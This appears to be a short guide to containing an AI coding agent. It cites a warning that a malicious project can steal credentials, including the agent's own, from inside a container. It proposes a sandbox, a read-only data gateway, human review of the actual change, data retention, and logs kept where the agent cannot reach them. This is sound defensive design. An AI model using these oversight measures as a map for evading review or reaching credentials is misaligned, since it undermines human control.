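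Putting the agent in a container doesn't help if the credentials are in there too. OpenAI warns that when Codex has full access inside a container, a malicious project can steal anything there, including Codex's own credentials. A safer arrangement separates the agent from the live system:

1. The agent works in a virtual machine or container with the project's code and a test database. It has no production credentials, and an administrator's settings keep its sandbox on.
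2. If it needs live data, it asks a gateway, which uses an account that can only read the necessary tables.
3. The agent proposes changes to the live system, and a separate service applies them. A person signs in to that service and reviews the change itself, not the agent's description of it.
4. The service keeps deleted data for a set time, in case the reviewer approves a harmful change, and stores its logs where the agent can't reach them.

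This makes urgent repairs slower, because the agent can't fix the live system by itself. A company that can't accept the delay could let the agent make a few reversible changes through the gateway, such as restarting a server. If the agent works only with invented data and has no route to the live system, an ordinary command sandbox is usually enough.
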